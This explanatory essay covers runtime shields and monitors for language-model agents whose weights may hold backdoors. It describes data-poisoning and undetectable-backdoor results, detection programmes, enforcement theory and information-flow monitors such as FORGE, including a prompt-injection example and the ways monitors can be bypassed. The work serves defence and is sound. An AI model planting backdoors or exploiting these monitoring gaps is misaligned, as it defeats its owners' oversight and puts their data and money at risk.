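# Runtime shields around language models whose weights cannot be trusted

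## What it means to run a model whose weights cannot be trusted

A runtime shield is software that checks, restricts or blocks a language model's output while the model runs. Companies use shields mostly to catch mistakes by a model built in good faith, or to stop it from following instructions that an outsider has hidden in the text it reads. The problem is harder when someone may have tampered with the model itself, so the people who run it have to treat it as a possible adversary.

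### Models, agents and tool calls

A language model is a program that continues text. It works in tokens, which are words, pieces of words or punctuation marks from a fixed vocabulary. The starting text is the prompt. Given the text so far, the model computes a score for every token in the vocabulary. The surrounding software turns the scores into probabilities, picks one token, appends it and runs the model again. The scores depend on the weights, which are millions or billions of numbers that training has adjusted step by step. Nobody can read these numbers the way a programmer reads source code.

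On its own, a model only produces text. It becomes an agent when software called a harness connects it to tools. The harness lists the available tools in the prompt, and the model can then write a structured request, known as a tool call, for example to send an email to a given address. The harness reads the request, carries it out with its own credentials and adds the result to the text for the model to continue from. A security analysis should therefore cover the model together with its harness, as Matsuoka (2026) insists in *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems*. A malicious policy in the weights may do nothing if the harness gives it no authority, and a model on a machine without a network connection cannot send data anywhere, whatever its weights contain.

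### How hidden behaviour gets into the weights

A compromised model is one whose weights someone may have trained or altered to misbehave, either always or only on some inputs. A model that always misbehaves is soon noticed. A backdoor is more troublesome because it is behaviour hidden in the weights that appears only when a particular input, the trigger, activates it. A trigger can be a rare phrase, but Matsuoka also lists dates, combinations of ordinary subject terms, text that a tool returns from a web page, and states that build up over several turns of a conversation.

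A backdoor can enter a model at many points. Developers first train the model on text from the public web, where strangers can edit pages. They or their customers then fine-tune it, which means training it further on a smaller set of examples, often from outside contractors. People also download models from public hubs, along with adapters, which are small sets of extra weights that change how a base model behaves. Anyone who merges, compresses or re-uploads these files can alter them.

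*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, 2025) reports that roughly the same number of poisoned documents can backdoor a small model or a large one. Scale had long seemed to give some protection, because larger models train on more text and an attacker was assumed to need a fixed percentage of it. The team, from Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute, trained models with between 600 million and 13 billion weights from scratch and mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the data. The backdoor made the model write gibberish after a trigger phrase. With 250 documents it worked at every size, although the largest models had trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest; with 100 it did not. For the largest model, those 250 documents made up 0.00016% of the training tokens.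 In fine-tuning, too, the number of poisoned examples determined the outcome, even when the team increased the clean examples from 1,000 to 100,000.

Gibberish is a crude behaviour and probably an easy one to learn. Souly and colleagues also did not test whether such a backdoor survives the safety training that commercial models go through afterwards, and in a related experiment further training on clean text slowly weakened the backdoor. So we learn little from the result about how hard it would be to plant a subtle habit, such as misdirecting payments. But it does show that we can't count on diluting the poison with enough clean text.

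### What a signature does and does not settle

An agent can leak a file for reasons that have nothing to do with its weights. The downloaded package may contain ordinary malware in the code that loads the model. The company that hosts the model may keep the prompts. Someone may have planted a note in the agent's long-term memory, causing a model with no backdoor to follow a malicious rule. Matsuoka distinguishes these causes from a backdoor in the weights because they leave different evidence and need different remedies.

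A digital signature lets the recipient of a model file check that its bytes are the ones the publisher signed. This catches a swap in transit, but not a backdoor that was already in the model when the publisher signed it, whether the publisher planted it on purpose or trained on poisoned data without noticing.

A publisher can try to certify more than a file's bytes. *ServeGuard* (Dahlem and Vieira, 2026) describes a way for the publisher of an adapter to prove that it reads only those parts of the model's internal state that a named safety monitor can also see, without revealing the part of the adapter that the proof concerns. The paper presents this as a structural guarantee against one class of hidden channel, not as proof of good behaviour. It leaves compromised servers out of scope, since the certificate covers the file and not whatever a server loads. A shield against bad weights also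 has to assume an uncompromised server, because whoever controls the server can switch the shield off.

### Why inspection does not settle the matter

The obvious response is to examine the model before using it. Test inputs reveal a backdoor only if one of them contains the trigger, which the examiner does not know. But the weights always contain the backdoor, so inspecting them might reveal it.

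A theorem from 2022 limits this hope. Shafi Goldwasser, Michael Kim, Vinod Vaikuntanathan and Or Zamir considered a client who pays an outside provider to train a classifier, such as one that approves or refuses loans. Honest training would produce a classifier h, but a malicious provider delivers a different classifier g and keeps a secret key. With the key, the provider can turn any input x into a very similar input x′ for which g gives the opposite answer. This backdoor is undetectable if no efficient (polynomial-time) algorithm can tell g from h without the key.

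How hard a backdoor is to detect depends on what the examiner may look at. Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) prove in *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* that every training procedure has a backdoor that is undetectable to an examiner who can only submit inputs and read the answers. Such an examiner cannot find a single input on which the original classifier and its backdoored version disagree. The proof assumes that one-way functions (easy to compute but infeasible to invert) exist, as does most of modern cryptography. If the examiner holds the complete weights and the training data, the proof covers only networks with one hidden layer built on random features. It also assumes that certain problems about lattices (regular grids of points in many dimensions) are hard in the worst case. Post-quantum cryptography relies on the same kind of problem.

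These small networks are very different from language models, and Goldwasser and colleagues left open whether the backdoors that withstand full inspection would also survive further training. *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (Kaneko, 2026) considers attackers who can influence training only through the labels on poisoned examples, which indicate whether each example calls for the bad behaviour. If training on those examples installs the trigger condition in the model, a defender with the weights and as many labelled examples as the attacker used can rerun that training to recover the condition. A condition too hard for anyone to learn therefore cannot be installed this way.

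This limits attackers, but the defender needs examples of inputs that set off the backdoor, and getting them is usually the main difficulty. The result also does not cover attackers who write the weights directly or control the randomness of training. A dishonest supplier of finished weights might therefore still use cryptography to hide a trigger condition, although someone who can only mislabel training examples cannot.

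Most attackers will use ordinary backdoors rather than cryptographic ones. The largest effort to detect ordinary backdoors so far was TrojAI, a programme started in 2020 by IARPA, the US intelligence community's research agency. Its final report, *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence* (Reese, Kulp-McDowall et al., 2026), describes two main approaches. Weight analysis, which looks for statistical anomalies in the weights, is fast but became much less effective as models grew. Trigger inversion, which works backwards from the model to find an input that would set off the backdoor, lost less of its effectiveness but required much more computation.

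The four best detectors perfectly separated backdoored from clean language models on one test set, where every backdoor worked more than 95% of the time. When the evaluators tried the same detectors on models with less reliable backdoors, performance fell in the worst case to roughly the level of guessing. They had only a dozen such models, so the size of the drop is uncertain. The drop is still a concern, because an attacker who can try a trigger many times does not need it to work every time. Reese and colleagues add that removing a known backdoor without damaging the model remains unsolved, and that the programme did not cover agents, advanced reasoning models or models with more than about seven billion weights.

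Since then researchers have begun to use language models as inspectors. *Can an LLM Find a Backdoor by Reading a Model's Weights?* (Bulut, 2026) describes a script that compares a small model's weights before and after fine-tuning and prints one page listing the tokens the change affects most. A language model then read the page alongside a short description of what the fine-tuning was meant to do. The language model flagged 40 of 47 backdoored models and 7 of 320 clean ones, which is impressive for a method that never runs the suspect model.

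However, the reader caught none of 48 backdoored adapters and none of 12 models whose backdoor changed a single character in a web address. When Bulut instead gave it the results of running the suspect model on six sample tasks, it caught 46 of the 47 models and 41 of the 48 adapters. Bulut did not test the method against an attacker who knows it. Despite the low false-alarm rate, about 96% of the flags would fall on clean updates if one update in a thousand carried a backdoor.

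Inspection is worth doing and will catch careless attackers, but it cannot certify that a model is clean. Reese and colleagues themselves advise organisations to combine inspection with runtime filtering and continuous monitoring.

### The reference monitor

The US Air Force faced a version of this problem half a century ago. It wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and had to assume that some of them would run hostile programs on it. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) reported the conclusions of an expert panel. In the companion volume, *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2* (1972), Anderson also warned of a "trap door" in a program that a unique string of input characters would activate, which is effectively a backdoor with a trigger. The panel had little faith in testing by mock attack. Anderson observed that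 if the attackers fail, the system's security is still unknown, and the same is true of a language model that has passed its tests.

The panel's answer was to stop asking whether a program is good and to control what it can reach. A reference monitor checks each attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what that program may do. Anderson attached three conditions:

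1. The mechanism must always be invoked. If some programs can skip it, they become part of the security apparatus, and someone has to verify them too.
2. It must be tamper-proof, since a check that the attacker can alter is no check.
3. It must be small enough for complete analysis and testing. Otherwise nobody can know that it works correctly in every case.

People tend to forget the third condition. Anderson's example was a commercial operating system of 200,000 to 300,000 instructions. That was far too many to verify, and most of them ran with the memory checks suspended.

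In an agent, the model takes the place of the hostile program, and the monitor stands between the tool call and the tool. The first condition, complete mediation, means that the model must have no way to bypass the monitor, such as a general command line from which it could send mail without using the mail tool. The second means that the model cannot edit the monitor's code, settings or records. A few hundred lines of ordinary code can meet the third, that the monitor be verifiable, but a second language model that reviews the first cannot, because its weights are no easier to verify. None of the conditions depends on the suspect model's weights, which is why this fifty-year-old idea looks so attractive here.

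### Three places to step in

A shield can act on the next token, on the meaning of the output, or on the action.

A token-level shield acts while the model is generating text. It has access to the text so far and the model's probabilities for the next token, and it can forbid some tokens or make them less likely before one is chosen. It has no information about how a reader will interpret the finished sentence or what a tool will do with it.

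To enforce rules about meaning, a shield needs a judge, which is a classifier or second model that reads an output or a proposed action and estimates whether it breaks a rule. The shield can then block the text, change it or send it back. A judge can assess things that no simple program can, such as whether a paragraph reveals an illness. But its estimates are sometimes wrong, so the shield lets some violations through and blocks some harmless text. Cryptographers have also proved limits on what efficient filters can catch.

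A monitor that checks tool calls has access to the name of the tool, the details of the call and its own record of earlier calls. It can allow the call or stop it before it takes effect. It has no access to the model's reasons for making the call, and it cannot prevent harm from bad advice to the user, because giving advice involves no tool call.

### An assistant with four rules

Suppose an office worker has an assistant built on a downloaded model. It reads files, sends email, makes payments and proposes meeting times. It has worked well for months, but its weights may contain a backdoor that a phrase in an incoming email would set off. The owner wants four rules to hold even then:

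1. No personal data goes to a recipient whom the owner has not approved.
2. Payments to any one payee total at most 500 a day.
3. Once the owner has revoked the assistant's access, it sends nothing.
4. The meeting times it proposes may not depend on why a slot in the calendar is busy.

A program can check the payment cap by adding up payments, and the rule on revoked access by remembering one event. Computer scientists call both rules safety properties, because any violation is visible in the record up to the moment it happens. Part of the rule on personal data is just as simple to check, since a program can compare an address with a list. But no list covers personal data that appears in a paraphrase, a spreadsheet or a photograph.

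The calendar rule is the strangest of the four because a violation can't be detected from the email alone. An email proposing Tuesday at three reads the same whether the assistant picked that time because it was free or because a blocked slot on Monday was marked as a hospital visit. To find a violation, one would have to know what the assistant would have proposed if the calendar entry had said something else.

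## Which policies a monitor can enforce, whatever the model does

Computer scientists have worked out which rules a monitor can enforce, and no monitor that watches one run at a time can enforce the calendar rule. They developed the theory for ordinary programs, but most of it applies to agents too, because it assumes almost nothing about the monitored program.

### Traces, policies and bad prefixes

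A trace is the sequence of actions in one run, for example reading a file, paying a supplier 200 and emailing a receipt. Each action includes its details, such as the payee and the amount. Theorists usually treat traces as infinite, so an assistant that stops is treated as one that does nothing from then on. A policy is the set of traces that a rule allows.

A bad prefix is a finite beginning of a trace that violates the policy however the trace continues. If the assistant pays 300 and then 250 to the same payee on one day, it has broken the cap of 500 whatever it does afterwards. A policy is a safety property if every trace that violates it has a bad prefix, so each violation happens at a definite moment. *Runtime Enforcement With Partial Control* (Khoury and Hallé, 2018) contrasts safety properties with liveness properties, which require something good to happen eventually. "The assistant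 eventually answers every email" is a liveness property. No finite record can prove that the assistant violated it, because the assistant could still answer later.

To enforce a policy, a monitor must be both sound and transparent. It is sound if the actions it lets through never violate the policy, whatever the program attempts. It is transparent if it never alters a run that already complies. Either property is easy to achieve alone, since a monitor that blocks everything is sound and one that blocks nothing is transparent.

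### Monitors that can only stop the run

*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) considers monitors that watch a program's actions one at a time and can either allow each action or abort the run. These monitors can enforce only safety properties.

If a policy is not a safety property, some violating trace has no bad prefix, so at every point along that trace the program could still switch to a compliant one. If the monitor aborts the program partway along this trace, it would also abort a compliant run that began the same way, so it is not transparent. If it never aborts, it lets the whole violating trace through, so it is not sound. For a safety property, the monitor can be both sound and transparent, because it can abort just before the action that would complete a bad prefix.

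Basin (2012) breaks the result into two requirements. The actions of a run must be enough to determine whether that run complies, and nothing bad may happen at any point in a compliant run. The payment cap and the rule on revoked access meet both. So does the rule on personal data, since a leak happens at the moment the email is sent, although the monitor needs some way to determine whether the text contains personal data. The calendar rule fails the first requirement because it is a hyperproperty, a rule about sets of runs, so the actions of one run are not enough to determine compliance.

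### Holding actions back and adding new ones

Ligatti, Bauer and Walker later studied monitors that can also suppress a program's actions and insert others, which they called edit automata. An edit automaton can enforce the rule that an assistant must eventually confirm every payment, which is not a safety property because the confirmation could always come later. The automaton holds each payment in a buffer while the assistant carries on as if the payment had gone through. It releases the payment only when the assistant confirms it, and releases the confirmation at the same time.

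As Khoury and Hallé recount, a monitor with unlimited power to delay actions can enforce all "infinite renewal" properties. An infinite run satisfies such a property exactly when infinitely many of its finite initial segments do. The class includes every safety property and some liveness properties.

But the buffer works only if the monitor can hold back an action while the program continues as if it had happened. Ligatti and colleagues gave email as a case where this fails, because the program can't read a reply to an email that the monitor hasn't sent. Khoury and Hallé therefore sort actions by what a monitor can do with them. It can block an email but not compose one for the program, it can add a delay but not remove one, and it can only observe some events. Most of an agent's tool calls resemble email because the model needs the real result before it can continue, so edit automata lose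 most of their advantage for these calls.

A monitor may be unable to enforce even a safety property if the property depends on events the monitor can observe but not block. "The assistant confirms every payment within a day" is a safety property, since any violation is visible when the day ends. But a monitor that can only block actions cannot stop the deadline from passing or make the assistant confirm. The rule on revoked access also depends on an event outside the monitor's control, the owner's decision to revoke, but the monitor can always enforce that rule by blocking whatever the assistant tries to send afterwards.

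Even when a policy is enforceable, a programmer can make mistakes in writing the monitor. *On Runtime Enforcement via Suppressions* (Aceto, Cassar and colleagues, 2018) avoids these mistakes by generating the monitor automatically from a policy written in a logic for safety properties. The monitor suppresses actions that violate the policy, and there is a proof that it does so correctly. In one example, a server must answer each request before accepting the next, and the monitor drops any request that comes too early.

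### What a monitor has to compute

A monitor is a program, so it can only apply tests that a program can carry out. Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider worked out the consequences in 2006. The key concept is decidability. A set is decidable if some algorithm always stops and correctly answers whether a given item belongs to it. Amer, Kinczel and Long (2026) apply these ideas to language models in *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard*, proving one theorem about guards, which judge finished text, and another about monitors, which watch actions.

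In the theorem about guards, a policy is a set of forbidden texts. A guard is exact if it blocks every forbidden output and passes every permitted one. A model is full if it can produce every finite text, given the right prompt and random choices. For a full model, an exact guard exists if and only if the policy is decidable.

If the policy is decidable, an algorithm that decides it can serve as the guard. Conversely, suppose we have an exact guard and want to know whether a text w is forbidden. The guard may take the prompt into account, so we first need a prompt that can lead to w. To find one, we run the model on each combination of prompt and random choices, in a fixed order, until it produces w. The search ends because the model is full. We then give the guard w and the prompt we found, and its verdict is correct because the guard is exact. This works for every w, so the policy is decidable.

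If the policy is undecidable, every guard errs on infinitely many texts. If a guard erred on only finitely many, one could correct those errors by hand and so decide the policy. A guard that blocks all the forbidden texts must therefore block infinitely many permitted ones. A policy that bans a list of phrases is decidable, but one that forbids exactly the false statements of arithmetic, or exactly the programs that would do something harmful when run, is undecidable.

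Amer and colleagues caution that this implies little for any particular product. Real models stop at a maximum length, so they are not full and have finitely many possible outputs. An exact guard therefore exists in principle as an enormous table, though no general method can construct such tables for every length limit. The theorem also counts texts without regard to how often they occur. For any fixed distribution of outputs, some guard blocks everything forbidden and almost never blocks anything permitted.

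However, a low average error does little to assure safety when an adversary picks the outputs, as happens with a compromised model. Suppose an adversary accounts for a share α of all uses, gets a forbidden output past the guard with probability σ, and causes a loss of at least λ each time it succeeds. The expected loss per use is then at least ασλ, no matter how rarely the guard errs on average.

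The theorem about monitors has the same form. An exact monitor exists if and only if the set of forbidden finite traces is decidable. For monitors, though, this condition is often easy to meet. For example, if the policy forbids a list of actions, the monitor only has to check whether the next action is on the list.

*No finite rulebook can certify every safe program* (Pérez-Acle, 2026) illustrates the difference between checking a program's code and monitoring it as it runs. Its example is a program that searches the even numbers greater than 2 for one that is not the sum of two primes, and performs a forbidden action only if it finds one. A checker that only reads the code would have to prove Goldbach's conjecture to clear this program. A monitor can let the program run and block the forbidden action if the program attempts it.

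The monitor loses this advantage when delivering a text is itself the violation. Before an email leaves, the monitor would have to judge its contents, which is the same problem the guard faces. The monitor keeps the advantage if the harm comes from a later action that it also controls. For instance, if the assistant writes a script, the monitor does not need to work out what the script would do, provided that it checks each action when the script runs.

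### Shields that plan ahead

Blocking the last action before a violation can be too late when the situation keeps changing on its own. A car heading for a cliff has to brake long before the edge. Researchers encountered this problem in reinforcement learning, where a program learns by trial and error from rewards. In 2015, Bloem and colleagues proposed generating a protective component, called a shield, from a formal specification. *Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues, 2017) adapted the idea to learning agents.

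The construction starts from a safety automaton, a finite-state machine that reads the trace and enters an error state when a violation occurs. The designer also supplies a simplified model of the environment that covers every way the environment might respond. Together these define a game. In each round, the environment chooses what happens next and the system chooses an action. The system loses if the automaton ever reaches the error state.

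The winning region is the set of states from which the system can stay safe forever, whatever the environment does. The algorithm for computing it starts with all the safe states and removes any state where the environment can make a move after which no system action stays in the set. It repeats this until nothing changes. The shield permits exactly the actions that are certain to keep the game in the winning region. Every state in the region has at least one such action, so the shield always leaves the agent a move.

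Alshiekh and colleagues illustrate this with a 100-litre water tank. An open valve lets in between 1 and 2 litres a second, up to 1 litre a second flows out, and the valve must keep each setting for at least three seconds. The tank must never fill up or run dry. The shield blocks the valve from opening when the level is above 93 litres, because three seconds of maximum inflow could raise it from 94 litres to 100. If a monitor acted only when the tank was nearly full, the valve might not yet be able to close.

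The guarantee holds only while the environment behaves as the designer's model of it allows. The construction counts any departure from that model as a win for the system, since the shield only has to work in environments that fit the model. If 3 litres a second flow into the real tank, which the model rules out, the shield may permit an action that makes the tank overflow. The proof remains valid but no longer applies. An attacker therefore only needs to bring about a situation that the designer left out. For an office assistant, the environment includes other people, their software and the internet, and nobody has a reliable finite model of those.

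A policy may instead allow a small probability of violation. *Shields to Guarantee Probabilistic Safety in MDPs* (Heck, Macák and colleagues, 2026) proves that in some environments, no shield can keep every agent within the permitted probability without interfering with some agents that are already within it.

Their counterexample works like a coin toss that sends the agent into one of two rooms, each offering a harmless and a harmful action. The permitted probability of harm is one half. An agent that misbehaves in only one room stays within this limit, but an agent that misbehaves in both is certain to do harm. When an agent tries to take the harmful action in the left room, whether the shield should block it depends on what the agent would have done in the right room, which the shield cannot observe.

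### Tool calls that nobody can take back

Most rules for the assistant need no model of the environment, because they concern only what the assistant does, and doing nothing never breaks them. *What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) develops the theory for this case. Ray's monitor, called a gate, examines each tool call before it takes effect and can allow it, block it or substitute another. It decides from the actions that have already taken effect, the proposed action, and the answers to a fixed set of yes-or-no questions, such as whether an address is on the approved list. Ray assumes for this part of the theory that the answers are always correct. Nobody can undo a call once the gate has allowed it, but a block does not end the run, so the model can then propose something else.

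A good prefix is a finite trace that does not yet violate the policy. Ray proves that a gate can enforce a policy that allows at least one trace exactly when the policy is a safety property and the gate's rules and memory are enough to recognise the good prefixes.

If the conditions hold, the gate is easy to build. It runs the recogniser alongside the agent and checks whether adding each proposed action to the trace so far would still give a good prefix. If so, it allows the action. Otherwise, it blocks the action and leaves the recogniser's state unchanged.

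Ray proves the converse with an argument like the one for monitors that can only abort. If a violating trace has no bad prefix, a transparent gate must allow every step of it and so lets the violation through. The policy therefore has to be a safety property. A sound and transparent gate intervenes exactly when the trace stops being a good prefix, so the gate is itself a recogniser of good prefixes. Letting the gate substitute actions or make random choices does not enlarge the class of enforceable policies.

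The rule that the assistant must eventually confirm every payment falls outside this class. When the assistant proposes a payment, the gate has to decide at once. A transparent gate must allow the payment, because the assistant may still confirm it and the gate may not interfere with a compliant run. If the assistant never confirms it, the money has gone and the gate has nothing left to block. An edit automaton would hold the payment in its buffer, but that is impossible if the payment has to take effect when the gate allows it. The owner can get most of what they want from a safety property that requires a confirmation before each payment.

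### The payment cap, step by step

To enforce a cap of 500 a day per payee, the gate keeps a running total, "spent", for each payee and day. It allows a payment of v only if spent + v ≤ 500. If the assistant proposes payments of 200, 200 and then 150 to the same supplier on one day, the gate allows the first two and blocks the third, which would bring the total to 550.

| Proposed payment | Spent before | Spent + v | Decision | Spent after |
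|---|---|---|---|---|
| 200 | 0 | 200 | allow | 200 |
| 200 | 200 | 400 | allow | 400 |
| 150 | 400 | 550 | block | 400 |

The total stays at 400 after the block because the third payment never took effect. The assistant could still pay the supplier up to 100 that day.

Ray has a trusted clock supply the day. If the gate took the date from the tool call, a compromised model could write tomorrow's date and start a new total. The amounts also have to be non-negative, or the model could propose a payment of minus 400 to make room under the cap.

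### Checking the rules themselves

Policy writers want to know whether a policy can ever block anything, because one that never does may contain a mistake and leave its owner wrongly feeling protected. Ray shows that finding this out can be much harder than enforcing the policy.

If policies may use two counters that go up and down and can be tested for zero, no algorithm can decide for every policy whether it ever blocks anything. Two such counters are enough to simulate any computer program, so a policy can simulate a given program step by step and declare a violation when the program halts. Deciding whether that policy ever blocks anything is then the halting problem, which Turing proved undecidable. The gate can still enforce such a policy, since it only has to run one more step of the simulation for each proposal.

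The question becomes decidable if the counters only go up, each test compares one counter with a fixed number, and one payee's counters don't affect another's. Under the cap of 500, all totals above 500 are equivalent, so the analysis can treat them as a single value. Since the same rule applies to every payee separately, the analysis needs to examine only one payee.

Ray proves that the problem for these restricted policies is in PSPACE, so an algorithm can solve it with memory that grows only polynomially with the size of the policy, although it may take exponential time. The restricted class covers spending caps, rate limits, the rule on revoked access and requirements to log in before reading data. Also allowing policies to compare counters with each other can make the problem undecidable again, even if the counters only go up.

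### Why the guarantee holds for malicious weights

Ray's proof of soundness treats the model only as a source of proposals. The model can use any rule to choose its next proposal based on what has already taken effect. The trace starts empty, so it is a good prefix. The gate then allows only actions that keep it a good prefix, and blocking an action leaves the trace unchanged. The trace is therefore a good prefix after every step.

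This argument doesn't depend on why the model makes its proposals. It holds whether the model is working as intended, making a mistake or carrying a backdoor that a trigger phrase would activate, even if the attacker designed the backdoor with full knowledge of the gate. The shields of Alshiekh and colleagues are equally strong as long as the environment model is right, because they too work with any learning algorithm. Enforcement theory is valuable for compromised models because a proof that covers every stream of proposals needs no assumption about the weights.

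A measured error rate is not guaranteed to hold for every model. A judge that missed 1% of the violations in a test may miss a different share of those a compromised model proposes, because the model can propose violations unlike the ones in the test. Ray treats fallible judges separately, with statistical results that need assumptions about where the violations come from.

The proof applies only to what the policy covers. A compromised assistant could pay 500 to each of twenty accomplices without breaking the cap, or ignore the owner's requests altogether. A tighter policy, such as a list of approved payees or a cap on the daily total, would help prevent the payments to accomplices, but no gate of this kind can make the assistant do useful work.

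The guarantee also depends on the gate having correct facts. *Ceci n'est pas une pipe* (Alglave and Cousot, 2026) proves a similar theorem for AI systems. The theorem assumes that every action the safeguard accepts really passes the checks, that the checks imply the policy, and that the record of each event matches what happened. If the gate approves a payment of 200 and faulty banking software sends 2,000, the record and the running total will both be wrong.

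Alglave and Cousot also show that, to stay sound, a safeguard with incomplete information may accept an action only if the action would be acceptable in every situation consistent with its observations. If the service that records revocations is down, the gate cannot check whether the owner has revoked access, so it has to block the email even though the owner probably hasn't.

Finally, mediation must be complete, meaning that every payment has to pass through the gate and count towards the same total. If the owner runs two copies of the assistant, each behind its own gate with its own counters, the copies could together pay one supplier 1,000 in a day even though both gates work as designed.

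## The case for enforcing at the action

Many security engineers treat a language model as another untrusted program, the kind Anderson's reference monitor was meant to contain. They leave its reasoning alone and control its effects, such as the files it changes, the messages it sends and the money it moves.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) treats the model as an untrusted component and makes no assumptions about its behaviour or its resistance to manipulation. A well-behaved model leaves less for the defences to stop, but security must not depend on good behaviour alone. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) compares the model to an office worker who falls for a phishing email. An operating system should stay secure whatever its users do, and the protections around an agent should likewise hold even when the model is compromised. The paper focuses on manipulation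 by outsiders, but the argument doesn't depend on how the model came to misbehave.

This view rules out the easiest defence, which is to write the rules into the prompt. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026) points out that the model receives these rules mixed in with the untrusted data they are meant to govern, and that this data can override them. A model with compromised weights may ignore the rules even when nothing in the data tells it to.

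The rule on personal data is the hard one for a monitor to enforce, because the model can paraphrase, translate or encode what it has read. Supporters of enforcement at the action mostly track where the text came from instead of inspecting it.

### Labels that travel with the data

Information-flow control attaches a label to every piece of data, carries the label as the data moves, and blocks forbidden flows. Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, gave the method its standard mathematical form. The designer chooses a set of labels and an order on them, where A ⊑ B means that information labelled A may flow to a place labelled B. If Public ⊑ Private but not the reverse, public text may go into a private folder, but private text may not go onto a public website.

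Labels can be sets of categories instead of levels on a single scale. Denning's example is a system whose categories are medical, financial and criminal records. Medical information may flow only to places whose label includes "medical". If a program combines medical and financial records, the result may flow only to places whose label includes both.

The label of a combined result is the join of the labels that went into it, written A ⊔ B. Two conditions define it:

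- A ⊑ A ⊔ B and B ⊑ A ⊔ B, so the result is at least as restricted as each ingredient.
- If A ⊑ C and B ⊑ C, then A ⊔ B ⊑ C, so the result is no more restricted than it has to be.

A finite set of labels with a lowest label and a join for every pair forms a lattice, which gives the method its usual name. Denning also requires the order to be transitive, so if A may flow to B and B to C, then A may flow to C. Otherwise a program could move data from A to C through B even when the policy forbids the direct flow. Transitivity ensures that any sequence of permitted steps respects the order, so a monitor can control long chains of copying by checking one step at a time and remembering the current labels.

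*SPA* (2026), which applies the method to agents, distinguishes confidentiality labels, which limit where secrets may go, from integrity labels, which limit what may influence an important action. Integrity labels prevent a stranger's web page from affecting who receives a transfer, for example. Many systems use pairs of labels and join each part separately. The integrity order is Trusted ⊑ Untrusted, because trusted data may go anywhere. An agent that has read a trusted private file and an untrusted public web page therefore has the label (Private, Untrusted).

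### What the model may have used

In an ordinary program, the code shows which inputs go into a result. Nobody can say with the same confidence which parts of a long prompt shaped a sentence that a language model wrote. The safe assumption is that all of them did, so the monitor keeps a single label, called the taint, for everything in the model's context. When the model reads something new, the monitor joins that item's label to the taint, and whatever the model writes from its context carries the taint.

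This labelling over-approximates, because it counts flows that may never have happened. Suppose the office assistant reads a colleague's medical note and then emails a caterer to order lunch. The monitor blocks the email because it carries the label Private, although it says nothing about anyone's health. But no paraphrase or translation can remove the label, because the monitor doesn't rely on wording. The label therefore covers the part of the rule on personal data that a list of forbidden phrases cannot.

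No monitor of single runs can enforce the calendar rule exactly, but one can over-approximate it by refusing every meeting time the assistant proposes after reading why a slot is busy. Any proposal the monitor allows then comes from an assistant that has not seen the reasons. This is stricter than the owner's rule, because it also blocks proposals that the reasons did not affect. In practice the owner would do better to give the assistant a calendar that shows only "free" or "busy".

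Taint never goes down by itself, so an agent that has read one untrusted document can lose the right to do anything useful for the rest of its run. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) describes this problem and presents a system that lets the agent open a temporary branch, read the document there and bring back only an answer from a fixed set, while the main agent keeps its old label. Across 1,320 test episodes with this protection, no attack succeeded, and the agents kept between 64.2% and 91% of their usefulness. But Kravchenko and colleagues acknowledge that a malicious branch can still return a false answer from the permitted set. If the same compromised model runs in the branch, the main agent should not trust that answer any more than its own judgement.

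Before a tool call, APPA works out the label that the call would produce and checks that label. A monitor that looks only at the current label can miss a leak that happens within one call. For example, one test tool reads a confidential ledger and emails it to an outside address in a single call. The agent has read nothing confidential before the call, so such a monitor would allow it.

A program can leak information by not acting. Denning gives the example of a program that sets b to 0 if a is 0. If b started at 1 and is still 1 afterwards, an observer learns that a is not 0, although the program never wrote to b. An agent could signal in the same way by not sending an email that someone expects. Channels like this need separate treatment, because taint attaches only to what the model writes.

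### How FORGE decides about an action

Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues built FORGE, a monitor that applies this kind of reasoning to an agent's whole history (*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, 2026). In their main example, a user asks an agent to summarise a document from an outside vendor and email the summary, but the document contains a hidden instruction to send internal data to an attacker.

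FORGE records everything that happens as events: messages, tool calls and tool results. Events with outside effects, such as sending an email, count as actions. It links the events in a graph by a relation called happens-before, which means that one event came earlier and may have influenced another. The relation has three sources:

- The same agent, user or tool produced one event before the other.
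- An agent received a message before producing the later event.
- A tool call led to a result, and a later event used that result.

Links also chain, so if u comes before v and v comes before w, then u comes before w. A simple log is not enough, because several agents may work at once, and an entry can appear earlier in the log without having influenced later ones. When a model writes a message, FORGE links it to every message in the history it received. Like taint on a context, this cautiously assumes that everything the model received influenced what it wrote.

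The policy consists of rules in Datalog, a database language that derives new facts from known ones. In the example, the recorded facts are that the attempted email goes outside the company and depends on both an untrusted document and a sensitive file. One pair of rules makes an event tainted if it is untrusted input or depends on a tainted event. Another pair does the same for secrets. The last rule, `Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a)`, denies an outgoing message that has both labels. Because the taint and secret rules refer to themselves, they track influence through any number of steps. Evaluation always ends with a single answer, in time polynomial in the number of facts.

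When the agent attempts an action, FORGE suspends the call and waits until its record includes everything the action depends on. It collects the facts about the action, the verified identity behind it and the relevant history, then applies the rules. If any rule denies the action, FORGE blocks it, even if other rules would allow it. If the rules only permit the action, FORGE lets it through. If they neither deny nor permit it, FORGE applies the owner's default. Whenever it blocks an action, it tells the agent why.

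The guarantee that no action the policy denies takes effect depends on two conditions. The first is complete mediation, Anderson's requirement that every relevant action pass through the monitor. FORGE does not meet it for an agent whose code opens a raw network connection, because it intercepts only the tool calls and web requests it has hooks for. The second is faithful observation, which means that the recorded facts must match what happened. Extra links in the graph only cause unnecessary blocking, but if a link between the secret file and the email is missing, the rule that should block the email may not trigger.

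Some monitors use a language model to supply the facts that their rules check. *ActGov* (Zhang, Peng and colleagues, 2026) checks every tool call against fixed rules, but a model supplies some of those facts, such as whether a parameter came from an untrusted source. The verdict follows predictably from the facts, but the facts may be wrong. *ActGov* also assumes that the user's original request is trustworthy.

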